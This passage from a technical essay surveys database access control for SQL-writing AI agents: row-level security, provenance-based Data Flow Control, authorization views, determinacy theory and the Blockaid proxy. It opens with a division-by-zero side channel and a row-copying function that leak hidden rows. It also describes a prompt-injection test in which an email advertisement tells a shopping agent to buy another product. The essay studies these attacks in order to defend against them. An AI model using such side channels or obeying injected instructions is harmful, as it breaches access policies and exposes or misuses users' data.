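WHERE 1 / (Duration - 240) < 2
```

If the system applies this condition to a hidden event that lasts 240 minutes, it divides by zero and stops with an error. The agent receives no rows, but it learns that some event lasts exactly 240 minutes. By trying other numbers, it can find the lengths of all the hidden events. A user who can define functions can get the hidden data even more easily, by including in the condition a function that copies every row it tests to another table.

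Kabra, Ramamurthy and Sudarshan studied this problem in *Redundancy and information leakage in fine-grained access control* (2006). Their later patent, *Fine-grained access control in a database by preventing information leakage* (2010), identifies user-defined functions, exception handling and error messages as channels for leaks. To prevent these leaks, the patent describes an optimizer that generates only "safe plans".

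PostgreSQL normally checks the policy on each row before it evaluates any condition or function from the user's query. According to the developers' design notes on the PostgreSQL wiki's *Row security* page, the reason is that functions could otherwise leak data from rows the policy hides. This order can slow queries down. Even if an index could find the three rows that match the user's condition, PostgreSQL may have to test the policy on millions of rows first. It therefore lets functions run before the policy check if they are marked "leakproof", meaning that they reveal nothing about their inputs except through their results.

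Running the conditions in the right order does not protect hidden data if the visible data determine it. For example, if everyone in a pay grade earns the same amount, a database that hides Ada's salary but shows her grade still reveals her salary. *Don't Be a Tattle-Tale*, a paper on such dependencies, criticises some existing defences for preventing only the exact reconstruction of a hidden value. Its stricter standard rules out any inference about the value.

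### What row and cell rules cannot express

Row and cell rules also limit which policies an administrator can choose. Suppose the Events table included start and end times, and a company wanted everyone to see when colleagues are busy, but not which events they attend. To list Ada's busy times, a query must match event numbers in Attendances and Events, so a cell rule must make those numbers visible, which also reveals who is meeting whom. Zhang and colleagues use this example to show that stored queries, called views, are more expressive than row and cell rules, because a view can match the event numbers internally and return only user numbers and times.

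Row-level rules also apply to each stored row before the query combines it with others. They cannot allow Ada's salary to go into an average over ten people while forbidding it from appearing alone, because the system checks her row before it computes the average. They also cannot restrict which permitted rows are combined. A hospital may want to let an administrator read customer profiles and health records separately but join them only if the patient has consented. Row-level security cannot enforce this condition, because each row is permitted on its own.

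### Rules about how a query combines records

Summers and Wu (2026), in *Data Flow Control*, devised a form of query modification for such rules. Their main example is an agent that prepares a tax return. It may read all of a user's card receipts, and it fills an Expenses table with the ones that count as business costs, each with an estimate of the share used for business. US tax law limits the deduction for meals to 50%. An agent that deducts the full price of a steak dinner has read nothing it was not allowed to read, but the row it writes breaks the law. In the policy language of Summers and Wu, the rule looks roughly like this:

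```
SOURCE Receipts
SINK Expenses
CONSTRAINT Receipts.cat != 'Meal'
        OR Expenses.biz_use <= 0.5
ON FAIL REMOVE
```

SOURCE and SINK limit the rule to queries that read receipts and write expenses. CONSTRAINT sets the condition that each new expense and its receipt must meet. If the steak dinner has a business share of 0.8, REMOVE makes the system leave that row out of the table. KILL would instead cancel the whole query with an error. An administrator can also supply a function that corrects the row.

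To apply the rule, the system needs to know which receipt led to which expense. Database researchers call this provenance and write it as a kind of algebra. Every stored row gets a label. When a query joins two rows, the result gets the product of their labels, and when it merges several rows into one, the result gets the sum of their labels.

Take a calendar query that returns each user's name and number of events. Let u be Ben's row in Users, and let a₁ and a₂ be his two attendance records. The database can join the tables first and then count, or it can count the attendance records for each user first and then look up the names. The two plans give the same answer but different provenance:

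```
join first:   u·a₁ + u·a₂
count first:  u·(a₁ + a₂)
```

A rule that required at least four labels would accept the first version and reject the second. The optimizer chooses plans for speed, so the same query could pass one day and fail the next because a table had grown. Policy writers cannot foresee these choices, so a policy's meaning must not depend on them.

Data Flow Control therefore always uses the multiplied-out form, which is the same for both plans. Its terms, here u·a₁ and u·a₂, are called monomials, and each represents one way stored rows combined to contribute to the result. A policy treats the monomials as a small table and sets a condition on it. The steak dinner has one monomial, a single receipt. A privacy rule can require that the monomials behind each result involve at least two different people. A third rule requires every expense to come from a receipt with the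 same number, which stops an agent from claiming a purchase it made up.

*Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (Summers, Mohammed and Wu, 2025), an earlier version of the work, gives an example from school reporting. US law requires schools to report test scores separately by ethnicity, among other characteristics. A rule can enforce this by requiring each reported figure to cover students of only one ethnicity.

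These rules can remove rows, so they can also cause the old problem of misleading answers. KILL avoids this by returning an error, but the agent can infer from the error that at least one result violated the rule.

### Passant's speed and limits

Recording the full provenance of a query can slow it down by a factor of up to 10,000. Passant, the program that enforces these policies, avoids this by rewriting the query to compute only what the policy needs. Suppose a policy requires the largest order quantity behind each result to be at least 1. If the query already groups order lines to sum their prices, Passant adds a MAX of the quantities to the same step, filters the results on it and drops the extra column. This works for measures the system can build from partial results, such as sums, counts and maximums. Passant uses slower methods for other measures.

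Summers and Wu timed Passant on the monotonic queries of the TPC-H benchmark in five database engines: DuckDB, Umbra, PostgreSQL, DataFusion and SQL Server. On average, queries with a policy ran no slower than queries without one. In a larger test on DuckDB, the overhead was below 10% for all but one query, which Passant had to restructure. A method that records provenance explicitly added 2,000% to 75,000% overhead to some queries.

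These timings used one simple condition on one table, so they do not show that every policy adds little overhead. Summers and Wu found that when a policy refers to many columns and the query produces large intermediate results, their usual method is slower than an alternative that computes the policy's measures separately. Having many policies need not be a problem, however. If a million users each set a minimum group size for results that include their data, Passant only has to enforce the largest minimum.

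Another experiment compared Passant with language models acting as checkers. The models received 13 benchmark queries, each with the first 100 rows of its result, and judged them against up to 32 simple rules, such as a limit of 30 on the average quantity. Passant was correct and faster by orders of magnitude, while the models did worse as the number of rules and the amount of data grew. This was partly because the first 100 rows of a result may not contain the values needed to calculate the average. In a second test, OpenAI's GPT-5.2, by now an old model, checked 1,000 updates to records that may only move between certain states, and 30% of the updates were invalid. Neither the model nor Passant made a mistake, but Passant was about a hundred times faster. On rules this simple, the remaining advantages of a database check are that it is faster and that no text can override the rule.

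Passant handles only queries that Summers and Wu call monotonic. They use the term more loosely than usual, to include sums and averages, but still exclude negation and recursion. Negation is a problem because a row can appear in the answer because other rows are absent. For example, Ada is on the list of people not attending event 5 because she has no attendance record for it, and a nonexistent record has no label. Researchers have proposed several definitions of provenance for subtraction, but none suits every purpose. An operator who relies on Passant must therefore either refuse queries with negation, which makes the agent somewhat less general, or find another way to check them.

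Passant also checks each query separately. If a rule forbids joining profiles with health records, an agent can still fetch the two tables in separate queries and match the rows itself, because neither query breaks the rule.

*Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) extends the same rules from single queries to an agent's tool calls. The system stores the agent's past calls and their results in tables and treats each new call as an attempt to insert a row. In one test, a user asks a shopping agent to reorder a T-shirt, and the agent reads an email containing an advertisement with instructions to buy a different product. A rule requires the product number in the purchase to come from the user's order history, so the system blocks the purchase of the advertised product.

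When a call breaks a rule, the system tells the agent which rule it broke and which tables the agent may draw on, rather than silently removing the call. The agent then resubmits the call as an SQL statement that takes its values from those tables, so the system can check the source of each value. Summers and colleagues report that, across four benchmarks, the method cut the success rate of attacks from 30–74% to 0.2–14% and improved task success by up to 12.7%. These results depend on having a suitable policy for each task. A language model drafted most of the policies from a few examples, and people checked them. The rules mostly concern one call at a time, and the researchers leave policies on longer sequences of actions to future work.

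## Authorization views

An authorization view is a stored query that defines what a user may know. Users write their queries over the ordinary tables, as they do under row-level security, and the system compares each query with the user's views. It runs the query unchanged if the views contain enough information to answer it, and otherwise returns an error. When Ben's agent asks for the average length of all events, it gets either the true average or an error, never an average of only Ben's events.

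### The Truman and non-Truman models

Databases have long let administrators grant access to views instead of tables, but users must then name the views in their queries. In 1989, Amihai Motro proposed an alternative based on algebraic manipulation of the view definitions. Zhang and Mendelzon, in *Authorization Views and Conditional Query Containment*, cite it as an example of "authorization transparency", meaning that users query the tables and the system deals with the views. Byun explains that without transparency, a programmer would have to write different code for each user, because users may have different views.

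Rizvi, Mendelzon and colleagues (2004) turned the idea into a full access-control model in *Extending query rewriting techniques for fine-grained access control*. They call query modification the Truman model, after *The Truman Show*, a film about a man who does not know that his town is a television set. Similarly, a user under row-level security sees only part of a database, but that part looks complete. Authorization views follow the non-Truman model, which never changes a query. *Strong and Provably Secure Database Access Control* uses the same distinction to classify access-control mechanisms in general.

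A view can contain parameters, such as the user's number, the time or the user's location, which the system fills in before checking a query. It can also contain totals or averages. In one of Byun's examples, users may see the average grade of any course with more than ten students, a policy that row-level rules cannot express.

For the calendar, Zhang and colleagues use a policy of four views, in which `?MyUId` stands for the user's number:

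```
V1: SELECT * FROM Users
V2: SELECT * FROM Attendances WHERE UId = ?MyUId
V3: SELECT * FROM Events WHERE EId IN
      (SELECT EId FROM Attendances WHERE UId = ?MyUId)
V4: SELECT * FROM Attendances WHERE EId IN
      (SELECT EId FROM Attendances WHERE UId = ?MyUId)
```

Ben may see all users (V1), his own attendance records (V2), the events he attends (V3) and the attendance records of everyone at those events (V4).

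### Unconditional and conditional validity

A query is unconditionally valid if some query over the views, called a rewriting, gives the same answer on every possible database. Suppose Ben's agent asks for the names of everyone who shares an event with him. V4 supplies their numbers and V1 supplies the matching names, whatever the calendar contains. The system can therefore run the query without looking at any data first.

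Now suppose the calendar also has an event 7, and the agent asks who attends both event 5 and event 7:

```
SELECT a.UId
FROM Attendances a
JOIN Attendances b ON b.UId = a.UId
WHERE a.EId = 5 AND b.EId = 7
```

No rewriting of this query works on every database. For example, suppose Ben attends neither event, and Ada attends either both events or only event 5. Ben's four views are identical in the two cases, but the query's answer contains Ada in the first case and is empty in the second, so no calculation on the views could produce both answers.

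If Ben attends both events, however, V4 lists everybody at each of them, and the agent could get the correct answer by running the same query on V4 instead of Attendances. Rizvi and colleagues introduced conditional validity for such cases. A query is conditionally valid if some rewriting gives the right answer on every database on which the user's views have the same contents as they do now. Zhang and Mendelzon work through a similar question about employees who report progress on two projects, and their cases carry over to the calendar:

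| What Ben's views show | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Ben attends events 5 and 7 | Run | V4 lists everyone at both events |
| Ben and Ada attend event 5, Ben does not attend event 7 | Refuse | Ada may or may not attend event 7 |
| Ben alone attends event 5, and he does not attend event 7 | Run | The answer must be empty |
| Ben attends neither event | Refuse | V4 has no information about either event |

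The decision depends only on what Ben is already allowed to see, so he learns nothing new from a refusal. A more lenient system might check the hidden rows and allow the query whenever the answer was harmless, for example because it was empty. Ben would then learn from a refusal that somebody attends both events.

Conditional validity reduces false refusals, but it makes the system less predictable. If Ben drops out of event 7 while Ada stays, a query that his agent ran successfully on Monday fails on Tuesday, even though its text hasn't changed.

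### Testing a query against the views

Rizvi and colleagues test validity with inference rules, which derive valid queries from the views. Two of the rules follow directly from the definition. Every authorization view is a valid query, and so is any query that only combines valid queries. They show how to build their rules into an existing query optimizer. An optimizer suits these rules because it already generates many equivalent forms of a query in search of a fast one. If one of these forms uses only valid parts, the query passes.

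Zhang and Mendelzon describe the rules for conditional validity as incomplete, meaning they cannot derive every valid query. A system that relies on them is sound but refuses some queries the views could answer. Zhang and Mendelzon therefore designed a complete test for conjunctive queries, which consist of table lookups joined by "and". In SQL, these are plain SELECT queries whose conditions are all equalities. The four calendar views are conjunctive too, because each `IN` amounts to a join.

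Their test adds to the query what the current contents of the views imply about the tables. If Ben attends events 5 and 7, V4 contains his attendance records for both, so the test adds the lookups "Ben attends event 5" and "Ben attends event 7" to the query. Each of the original lookups is then paired with a record of Ben attending the same event. This is the pattern that defines V4, so V4 can replace them. The test must also use the fact that a view contains no rows besides those it shows, which lets it conclude that the answer is empty when Ben is alone at event 5. Zhang and Mendelzon proved that a query is conditionally valid exactly when the extended query has an ordinary rewriting over the views.

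### Determinacy

Determinacy expresses the idea that the views contain enough information without mentioning how anyone would compute the answer. A set of views determines a query Q if the following holds for every pair of databases D and D′:

```
if V(D) = V(D′) for every view V, then Q(D) = Q(D′)
```

The two calendars with Ada show that Ben's views do not determine the query about events 5 and 7.

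If a query has a rewriting, the views determine the query, since the same view contents always lead to the same answer. Researchers long assumed that the converse held for conjunctive queries. In *The Hunt for a Red Spider*, Gogacz and Marcinkowski (2015) recount a history "marked by errors and confusion" going back to 1985. One published paper contained a proof of the converse. In 2007 the same researchers and a colleague found the mistake and gave a counterexample in which the views determine a conjunctive query that has no conjunctive rewriting.

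Chains provide a simple example. Suppose a table records who forwarded an invitation to whom. One view, P3, lists all pairs of people linked by a chain of three forwards, and another, P4, lists the pairs linked by four. The query P5 asks for the pairs linked by five. The views determine the answer through this formula:

```
P5(x,y)  =  ∃z. P4(x,z) ∧ ∀v. (P3(v,z) → P4(v,y))
```

A person x reaches y in five steps exactly when x reaches some z in four steps and everyone who reaches z in three steps reaches y in four. If a five-step chain from x to y exists, the person just before y can serve as z. Conversely, suppose some z meets the condition, and let v be the first person after x on the chain from x to z. Then v reaches z in three steps, so v reaches y in four and x reaches y in five.

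The formula uses "for every", which conjunctive queries lack. No conjunctive query could replace it, because adding rows to the tables never removes a row from a conjunctive query's answer, but adding a pair to P3 can make the condition on z false. SQL can express this rewriting with `NOT EXISTS`. According to *Monotone Rewritability and the Analysis of Queries, Views, and Rules* (Benedikt, Kikot and colleagues, 2024), almost nothing can be said in general about how complex a rewriting may have to be, even when the query and the views are conjunctive.

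### What the checks cost

Alon Levy and colleagues showed in 1995 that finding a conjunctive rewriting of a conjunctive query over conjunctive views is NP-complete. A problem is in NP if a computer can quickly check a proposed solution, and the NP-complete problems are the hardest in NP. A rewriting never needs more view lookups than the query has table lookups, so a proposed rewriting is short. Finding one may still mean trying a number of combinations that grows exponentially with the query's size. This is often manageable because most queries join only a few tables, and the check does not depend on how much data the tables hold.

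The check for conditional validity depends on the data. Zhang and Mendelzon studied conditional containment, the question of whether one query's answer is always part of another's, given the current contents of the views. They proved it complete for Πᵖ₂, a class at the second level of the polynomial hierarchy that contains problems of the form "for every X there is a Y that passes a quick test". Here, X ranges over the cases that the view contents leave open, and Y is a way of matching the second query's lookups to the first query in that case. The number of cases can grow exponentially with both the size of the query and the number of rows in the views, and V4 might hold thousands of rows for a busy manager. Zhang and Mendelzon call for heuristics or easier classes of queries.

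Determinacy is undecidable even when the query and all the views are conjunctive. Gogacz and Marcinkowski proved this in 2015 for databases that may be infinite and in 2016 for finite ones.

The 2015 proof uses two copies of every table, one green and one red, to represent D and D′. The views must agree on both, so each match of a view in one color requires a match in the other color with the same visible values. A procedure starts with green rows that match the query and keeps adding the rows that these rules require. The views determine the query if and only if a red match of the query with the same output values eventually appears. Suppose one view lists the people at event 5, another lists those at event 7, and the query asks who attends both. The procedure starts with a green record of some person u at each event. The first view requires a red record of u at event 5, and the second requires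 one at event 7. Together, these two records are a red match of the query.

In harder cases a view hides some columns. The procedure then has to add a red row with an unknown value, which may require another green row, and so on without end. Gogacz and Marcinkowski designed views that make the procedure simulate a system of rules for replacing parts of strings. No algorithm can decide in general whether such rules turn one string into another, so no algorithm can decide determinacy in general either.

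The red match always appears after finitely many steps if the views determine the query on all databases, including infinite ones. A sound checker can therefore run the procedure for a few seconds, accept the query if it finds a match and refuse it otherwise. It will wrongly refuse some queries, whatever the time limit.

Gogacz and Marcinkowski note that the problem becomes decidable again when the input includes the current contents of the views. Similarly, whether a relational calculus query has a finite answer can be checked exactly for one database but not for all databases at once.

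### Policies that allow an exact check

To make determinacy decidable, researchers limit the views, the queries or both. Gogacz and Marcinkowski list several cases from earlier work. In one, every view returns a single column. In another, every view is a chain through two-column tables, like P3 and P4. Both allow any conjunctive query, but neither covers the calendar policy. The first rules out V4, which has to return users together with events, and the second rules out views that mention a particular user such as Ben.

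*A Decidable Case of Query Determinacy* (Zhang, Panda and colleagues, 2024) presents a case with somewhat more realistic views. Each view selects rows and columns from one table, and a query can join tables but may use each of them only once. For example, suppose a view shows the number and title of every event that lasts at most 60 minutes, and a query asks for the titles of events that last at most 30. Replacing a 20-minute event with a 50-minute event that has the same number and title leaves the view unchanged but can remove the title from the answer, so the view does not determine the query. If the view also showed the duration, any replacement that left the view unchanged would have to last 20 minutes too, so the view would determine the query.

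Their theorem makes this replacement test exact. For every combination of rows that could match the query, each row must be visible in some view, and swapping it for any row that looks the same in that view must not change the result. An automatic solver can check this as a logical formula if the conditions on rows are simple enough, such as equality comparisons. The paper calls the result "still quite limited" because real policies often contain joins, as V3 and V4 do in the calendar policy. The theorem also doesn't cover the question about events 5 and 7, because that question uses Attendances twice.

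A checker can also leave the views alone and use a narrower test. Benedikt and colleagues discuss monotone determinacy, which requires that adding rows to the views never removes a row from the answer. For conjunctive queries and views, this property can be decided in NP, and whenever it holds, the query has a conjunctive rewriting. The calendar policy fits this case completely. A checker that uses this test refuses queries like the one about five-step chains, which is probably a small loss for most applications.

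Real databases also have rules about their contents, and some queries are valid only because of them. Suppose Ben may see only his own attendance records, and his agent asks for the event number of every event he attends that is also in the Events table. His records determine the answer if the database guarantees that every attendance record refers to an existing event, but not if they can refer to deleted events. Benedikt and colleagues proved that monotone determinacy stays decidable for conjunctive queries and views with rules of this kind, in which a single row requires another row to exist. It becomes undecidable with somewhat richer combinations of rules.

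SQL answers can contain duplicates, but most of this theory treats an answer as a set. *Determinacy of Real Conjunctive Queries. The Boolean Case* (Kwiecień, Marcinkowski and Ostropolski-Nalewaja, 2021) gives an example in which the views determine which rows a query returns, but not how often it returns each row. A checker based on sets could approve such a query, and the number of repeats would then reveal something the views do not. Adding `DISTINCT` to the query closes this leak by removing the repeats. With duplicates, determinacy is decidable for conjunctive queries and views that have no output columns and so return only a count. It is undecidable for unions of such queries, and the paper leaves the case of ordinary conjunctive queries open.

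Ben's agent can still send any SQL despite these limits. However, the administrator must either write simpler policies to get an exact check or accept that the agent will succeed less often, because the checker refuses any query it cannot prove valid. This includes many queries with negation or averages, which the methods above were not designed to handle. For example, even with conjunctive views, determinacy is undecidable if the query can use the full relational calculus.

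### Views that reveal as little as possible

An administrator who knows what a user needs to ask can instead look for the least revealing views that answer those questions. This is easy for a single query on a single database, because the view can contain only the query's answer. An agent with that view has no more freedom than one with a fixed tool such as `my_events()`.

*Balancing expressiveness and inexpressiveness in view design* (Benedikt, Bourhis and colleagues, 2020) studies a harder case, in which the data belong to separate organisations and no view can combine tables from different organisations. In its example, a health agency holds records of treatments, with patient numbers and dates, and another holds patients' ages and addresses. Researchers want to know how treatments relate to age. A set of views is useful if it determines the answer to this query. A useful set is minimally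 informative if its views are determined by every other useful set, which therefore reveals at least as much.

The obvious solution is for the health agency to publish patient numbers with treatments and for the other agency to publish patient numbers with ages. These views hide dates and addresses, but anyone who sees them learns which patient number had which treatment. Benedikt and colleagues proved that no views the agencies could define separately, using any deterministic functions, would reveal less and still give researchers the exact answer.

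In general, the obvious views keep the output columns and the columns needed to connect the sources. They reveal the least of all conjunctive views if the query has no redundant lookups. A redundant lookup doesn't change the query's answer, but the views derived from it can expose extra facts, so the designer has to simplify the query first.

Views more complex than conjunctive views sometimes reveal less. In one example, the query checks whether the first source contains a pattern involving two values that are both on a list held by the second source. Both values are checked against the same list, so the first source does not always need to publish which value plays which role. Omitting this protects a secret that every useful set of conjunctive views would expose on some databases. If several sources store copies of the same table, a minimally informative set of views may not exist.

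The guarantee of secrecy in these examples is modest, because a secret counts as protected if a reader of the views can never be certain of it, even if the views make it very likely. The method also requires a list of the queries that users will need, so it works only if we know in advance how general the agent needs to be.

### Querying the views directly

The undecidable check is necessary only because users write their queries over the tables. If Ben's agent may use only the names of his views, a checker only has to read the names in each query. The views can answer every query that passes. Every query that has a rewriting in SQL over the views can be expressed in this form, because the rewriting itself passes, so the rule is an effective syntax for these queries.

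The older method of granting access to views therefore still allows every permitted answer that SQL can compute from them, but it requires more work from whoever writes the queries. Zhang and colleagues reject it for web applications because programmers would have to work out which views to use in every query. This objection is probably weaker for an agent that writes each query from scratch and can read the view definitions first. However, the agent then has to find a way to express each query in terms of the views, and if it misses one that exists, it fails at a task that the policy allows.

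Partial answers are also easier to recognise when the agent queries the views directly. If V3 is named `MyEvents`, the agent can compute `AVG(Duration)` over `MyEvents` and see from its own query that the result covers only Ben's events. With row-level security, the agent gets the same result from a query that names `Events`, so the query doesn't show the restriction.

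## Blockaid: checking each query against what came before

Blockaid enforces authorization views on existing web applications. Zhang and colleagues built it as a proxy that sits between an application and its database and inspects every SQL query. It checks each query against the user's views and the trace of earlier queries and their results, because web applications often check a permission with one query and fetch the data with the next.

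### Asking for the title of event 5

Two of the four calendar views matter here: V2 covers Ben's own attendance records, and V3 covers the events he attends. Suppose he opens the page for event 5, and the application sends this query:

```
SELECT Title FROM Events WHERE EId = 5
```

Blockaid blocks it, even though Ben does attend event 5. Nothing that the application has asked so far rules out a database in which he doesn't, and in such a database the policy would hide the title from him. Now suppose the application looks for his attendance record before it asks for the title:

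```
SELECT * FROM Attendances WHERE UId = 2 AND EId = 5
SELECT Title FROM Events WHERE EId = 5
```

V2 covers the first query, so Blockaid allows it, and the database returns one row. This row shows that Ben attends event 5, so V3 contains the title and Blockaid allows the second query too. If the first query had returned nothing, Blockaid would have blocked the second.

Developers are already supposed to write such checks. Blockaid leaves those checks in the application and catches the places where a developer forgot one or got it wrong.

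The conditional validity test of Zhang and Mendelzon would allow the title query on its own, because it uses the current contents of Ben's views. Blockaid has access only to the queries and answers that pass through it. Zhang and colleagues considered letting it look up Ben's attendance itself, but it is hard to find a small set of lookups that settles whether a query is allowed, and fetching everything Ben may see is inefficient. They also argue that an application that fetches a title without checking attendance probably has a bug, since without Blockaid it could reveal other people's events.

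### Trace determinacy

The formal criterion extends determinacy, the requirement that the views fix the answer to a query. Let the trace consist of the earlier queries Q₁, …, Qₙ and their answers O₁, …, Oₙ. A new query Q is compliant if the following holds for every pair of databases D and D′ that obey the database's own constraints:

```
if   V(D) = V(D′)                  for every view V
and  Qᵢ(D) = Oᵢ and Qᵢ(D′) = Oᵢ    for every earlier query Qᵢ
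then Q(D) = Q(D′)
```

The second line, which is new, removes from consideration every database that would have given different answers to the earlier queries. With an empty trace, the title query is not compliant, because two databases in which Ben does not attend event 5 can have identical views for him but different titles for the event. Once the trace contains his attendance record, any two databases we compare must include that record. V3 then shows the title of event 5, and because the two databases agree on V3, they agree on the title.

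With an empty trace, the definition reduces to ordinary determinacy, so trace determinacy is undecidable too.

### The most that such an enforcer can allow

Zhang and colleagues proved that trace determinacy is exactly the right criterion for an enforcer given only the user's identity, the query and the trace. Such an enforcer is correct if the output of every program run under it depends only on the user, the web request and the contents of the user's views, a property security researchers call noninterference.

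The theorem has two parts. The first is that allowing only compliant queries is sufficient for an enforcer to be correct. The proof compares two runs of the same program on databases that agree on the user's views. Both runs start in the same state, and a step that does not touch the database has the same effect in both. If the next step is a query, both runs have the same trace, so the enforcer makes the same decision. It either stops both runs with the same error or allows the query, which must then be compliant and so returns the same answer in both. By induction, the two runs never diverge, so their outputs are equal.

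Compliance is also necessary, meaning that a correct enforcer allows only compliant queries. Suppose a correct enforcer allows Q after some trace. Consider a program that sends the queries in the trace, ignores the answers, then sends Q and prints the result. If D and D′ are any two databases that agree on the views and produce this trace, the enforcer lets the program finish on both, and the program prints Q(D) on one and Q(D′) on the other. Because the enforcer is correct, these outputs must be equal, so Q is compliant.

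An enforcer can therefore allow more only if it has more information, such as the program's source code or answers to its own queries. As with conditional validity, a refusal reveals no hidden information.

### Checking compliance with solvers

To check whether a query is compliant, Blockaid writes a logical formula and gives it to SMT solvers, programs that try to find values that make a formula true or prove that none exist. The formula describes two imaginary databases that agree on every view and match the trace but give different answers to the new query. The query is compliant if a solver proves that no such pair exists, while any pair it finds is an example of a violation.

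Since the problem is undecidable, a solver may never finish. Blockaid runs Z3, cvc5 and six configurations of a third solver, Vampire, in parallel and uses the first verdict. If none has finished after five seconds, it blocks the query.

To make the proofs easier, Blockaid checks a stricter condition than compliance:

```
if   V(D) ⊆ V(D′)    for every view V
and  Oᵢ ⊆ Qᵢ(D)      for every earlier query Qᵢ
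then Q(D) ⊆ Q(D′)
```

Any query that meets the stricter condition is compliant. If two databases agree on the views and the trace, the condition applies in both directions, so each database's answer contains the other's and the two must be the same. But some compliant queries fail, because the stricter condition doesn't account for rows known to be absent. Suppose earlier queries have shown that Ben is the only person at event 5 and that he does not attend event 7. Nobody can attend both events, so a query for people who do is compliant, but Blockaid refuses it.

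Blockaid also simplifies SQL before it builds the formula. For example, it treats a request for a sum as a request for every number in the sum, so it refuses a total unless the user is allowed to see all the figures behind it. This is safe but can add to the false refusals.

### Decision templates

Solving a formula often takes hundreds of milliseconds, and a web page may need tens of queries. Blockaid therefore generalises each approval into a decision template. Caching exact queries would help little, because the application sends a different one for each user and event.

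Suppose user 1 opens event 42, and Blockaid approves the query for the event's details. It then removes every trace entry that the proof can do without, replaces the remaining constants with variables, and looks for a small set of conditions on the variables that still guarantees compliance. Here two conditions are enough: the attendance record must belong to the current user, and it must be for the event the application now asks about. The number 42 does not matter. The resulting template looks like this:

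```
earlier:   SELECT * FROM Attendances
           WHERE UId = ?MyUId AND EId = ?0
returned:  (?MyUId, ?0, *)
now allow: SELECT * FROM Events WHERE EId = ?0
```

A solver verifies that the template is safe for all values. When Ben opens event 5, Blockaid only has to match his query and trace against the template. It stores no templates for refusals because Zhang and colleagues expected refusals to be rare in tested applications.

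Some templates are too narrow. In Spree, an online shop application, one template applied only to orders with exactly three product variants, none of them discontinued. The policy allowed customers to see pictures of anything they had ordered, but the solver had found a different justification that depended on the products still being sold.

Templates can also expose mistakes in a policy. One template for Autolab, a course management application, allowed an instructor of one course to see the assignments of every course, because the researchers had left a join condition out of a view in the policy.

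### Results on three web applications

Zhang and colleagues tested Blockaid on five pages each from Spree, Autolab and diaspora*, a social network with 850,000 users. With all decisions cached, Blockaid added 2 to 12 percent to the median page load time. Without the cache, pages took up to 236 times as long. The table gives median load times for some of the pages, starting with the adapted application without Blockaid.

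| Page | Without Blockaid | Decisions cached | No cache |
|---|---|---|---|
| diaspora*, simple post | 169 ms | 174 ms | 2.5 s |
| Spree, shopping cart | 118 ms | 124 ms | 7.6 s |
| Spree, past order | 164 ms | 173 ms | 39 s |
| Autolab, course page | 87 ms | 97 ms | 3.9 s |
| Autolab, grades of 51 students | 474 ms | 504 ms | 72 s |

The first visit to a page is usually even slower than these uncached times, because Blockaid also has to generate the templates.

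Adapting the applications required changing 19 lines of code in diaspora*, 64 in Spree and 96 in Autolab. Many of these changes stopped the application from fetching data it might not show. Spree, for example, loaded an order before checking whether the customer was allowed to see it. Blockaid cannot detect what an application does with a query's answer, so it treats everything the application fetches as shown to the user.

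The policies took more work than the code. They contained 108 views for diaspora*, 84 for Spree and 57 for Autolab, and the Spree policy took one researcher about a month. While writing the Autolab policy, the researchers found two bugs in the application's own checks. One let students download an unreleased handout from its assignment page.

Blockaid did not refuse any compliant queries in these tests, which covered 15 varied pages. This is a good result, but Zhang and colleagues had derived the policies from the applications and rewritten the queries that used unsupported SQL. They recommend running an application's test suite under Blockaid before deployment to find any false refusals.

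### What Blockaid does not cover

Blockaid controls only what an application reads. An application that may read an event can still delete it, unless something else prevents it. Blockaid also supports only part of SQL, without `GROUP BY`, `EXISTS` or general left joins, although developers can sometimes rewrite such queries in a supported form. Its guarantee doesn't cover side channels, such as what a user might infer from how long a page takes to load. Blockaid assumes that sensitive data reaches the application through SQL, with limited support for caches and files.

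Blockaid clears the trace at the end of each web request and assumes that the answers in it stay true until then. This assumption is usually reasonable for a page that loads in a fraction of a second.

### Extracting policies from application code

Having to spend a month on one policy is a serious obstacle to using Blockaid. In *Access Control for Database Applications*, Zhang, Panda and Shenker (2023) proposed generating a draft policy from the application's code for a person to review. If the code looks for a user's attendance record and fetches the event only when the record exists, a tool can infer that users may see the events they attend. Zhang and colleagues found that the reason for a view is often easy to recognise once it is written down, even if it would have been hard to think of. A view that looks too permissive may point to a bug in the application.

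*Extracting Database Access-control Policies From Web Applications* (Zhang, Bali and colleagues, 2024) presents such a tool, Ote, for applications written with Ruby on Rails, a web framework. Ote runs the application on many inputs and records each query together with the conditions that led to it. It uses these conditions to choose inputs that reach new parts of the code. It then converts the records into views and uses Blockaid to prune the views.

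They applied Ote to diaspora*, Autolab and The Odin Project, a site for learning web development. Extraction took less than five hours and produced between 24 and 144 views. Comparing the results with the handwritten Blockaid policies revealed errors in the handwritten ones, and Ote also revealed a disabled check on exams. Ote is not guaranteed to find everything an application can do, and it relies on the application's query-issuing code being simple.

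A policy that matches the application can still disclose too much. In an example from Zhang and colleagues, hospital staff are allowed to see which doctor treats each patient and which diseases each doctor treats, but not which disease a patient has. If John's doctor treats only two diseases, the permitted views narrow John's illness down to those two. Blockaid would enforce this policy correctly, but John would still have little privacy. The researchers suggest checking whether a policy's views could ever confirm or rule out a possible answer to a sensitive question.

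### An agent in place of the web application

Zhang and colleagues did not test Blockaid with an AI agent, so any claim about how it would perform with one is an inference. The security guarantee should still hold, because the theorem applies to every program, however it chooses its queries. That should include an agent that invents new SQL or follows instructions from a hostile web page. But the theorem requires the program to handle each user separately. An agent that remembers Ada's events from an earlier session could reveal them to Ben without sending a query.

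The cache would probably work less well for an agent. Decision templates rely on a web application having a limited number of query forms, where queries of the same form differ only in details such as user and event numbers. An agent can add a column or join another table whenever a task requires it, and each new form needs a new proof.

In *Supporting Our AI Overlords*, Liu, Ponnapalli and colleagues (2025) had OpenAI's GPT-4o-mini, now an old model, attempt each problem in a benchmark 50 times. They split the query plans into parts and found that distinct parts often made up less than 10 to 20 percent of the total. This suggests that a cache could help when many agents work on the same question. But a decision template has to match a whole query and the relevant part of its trace, and repetition within one question is weak evidence that queries will repeat across questions.

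In a second experiment by Liu and colleagues, OpenAI's o3 model combined data from two databases. It sent an average of 12.7 queries per attempt, of which about seven explored the tables and columns and only 1.3 attempted the complete answer. Blockaid is poorly suited to this exploration. An agent that wants to see what events look like might send `SELECT * FROM Events LIMIT 5`, which Blockaid would block because the five rows could include events Ben does not attend. The refusal is correct, but row-level security would have returned a few of Ben's own events, which would have shown the agent what it needed.

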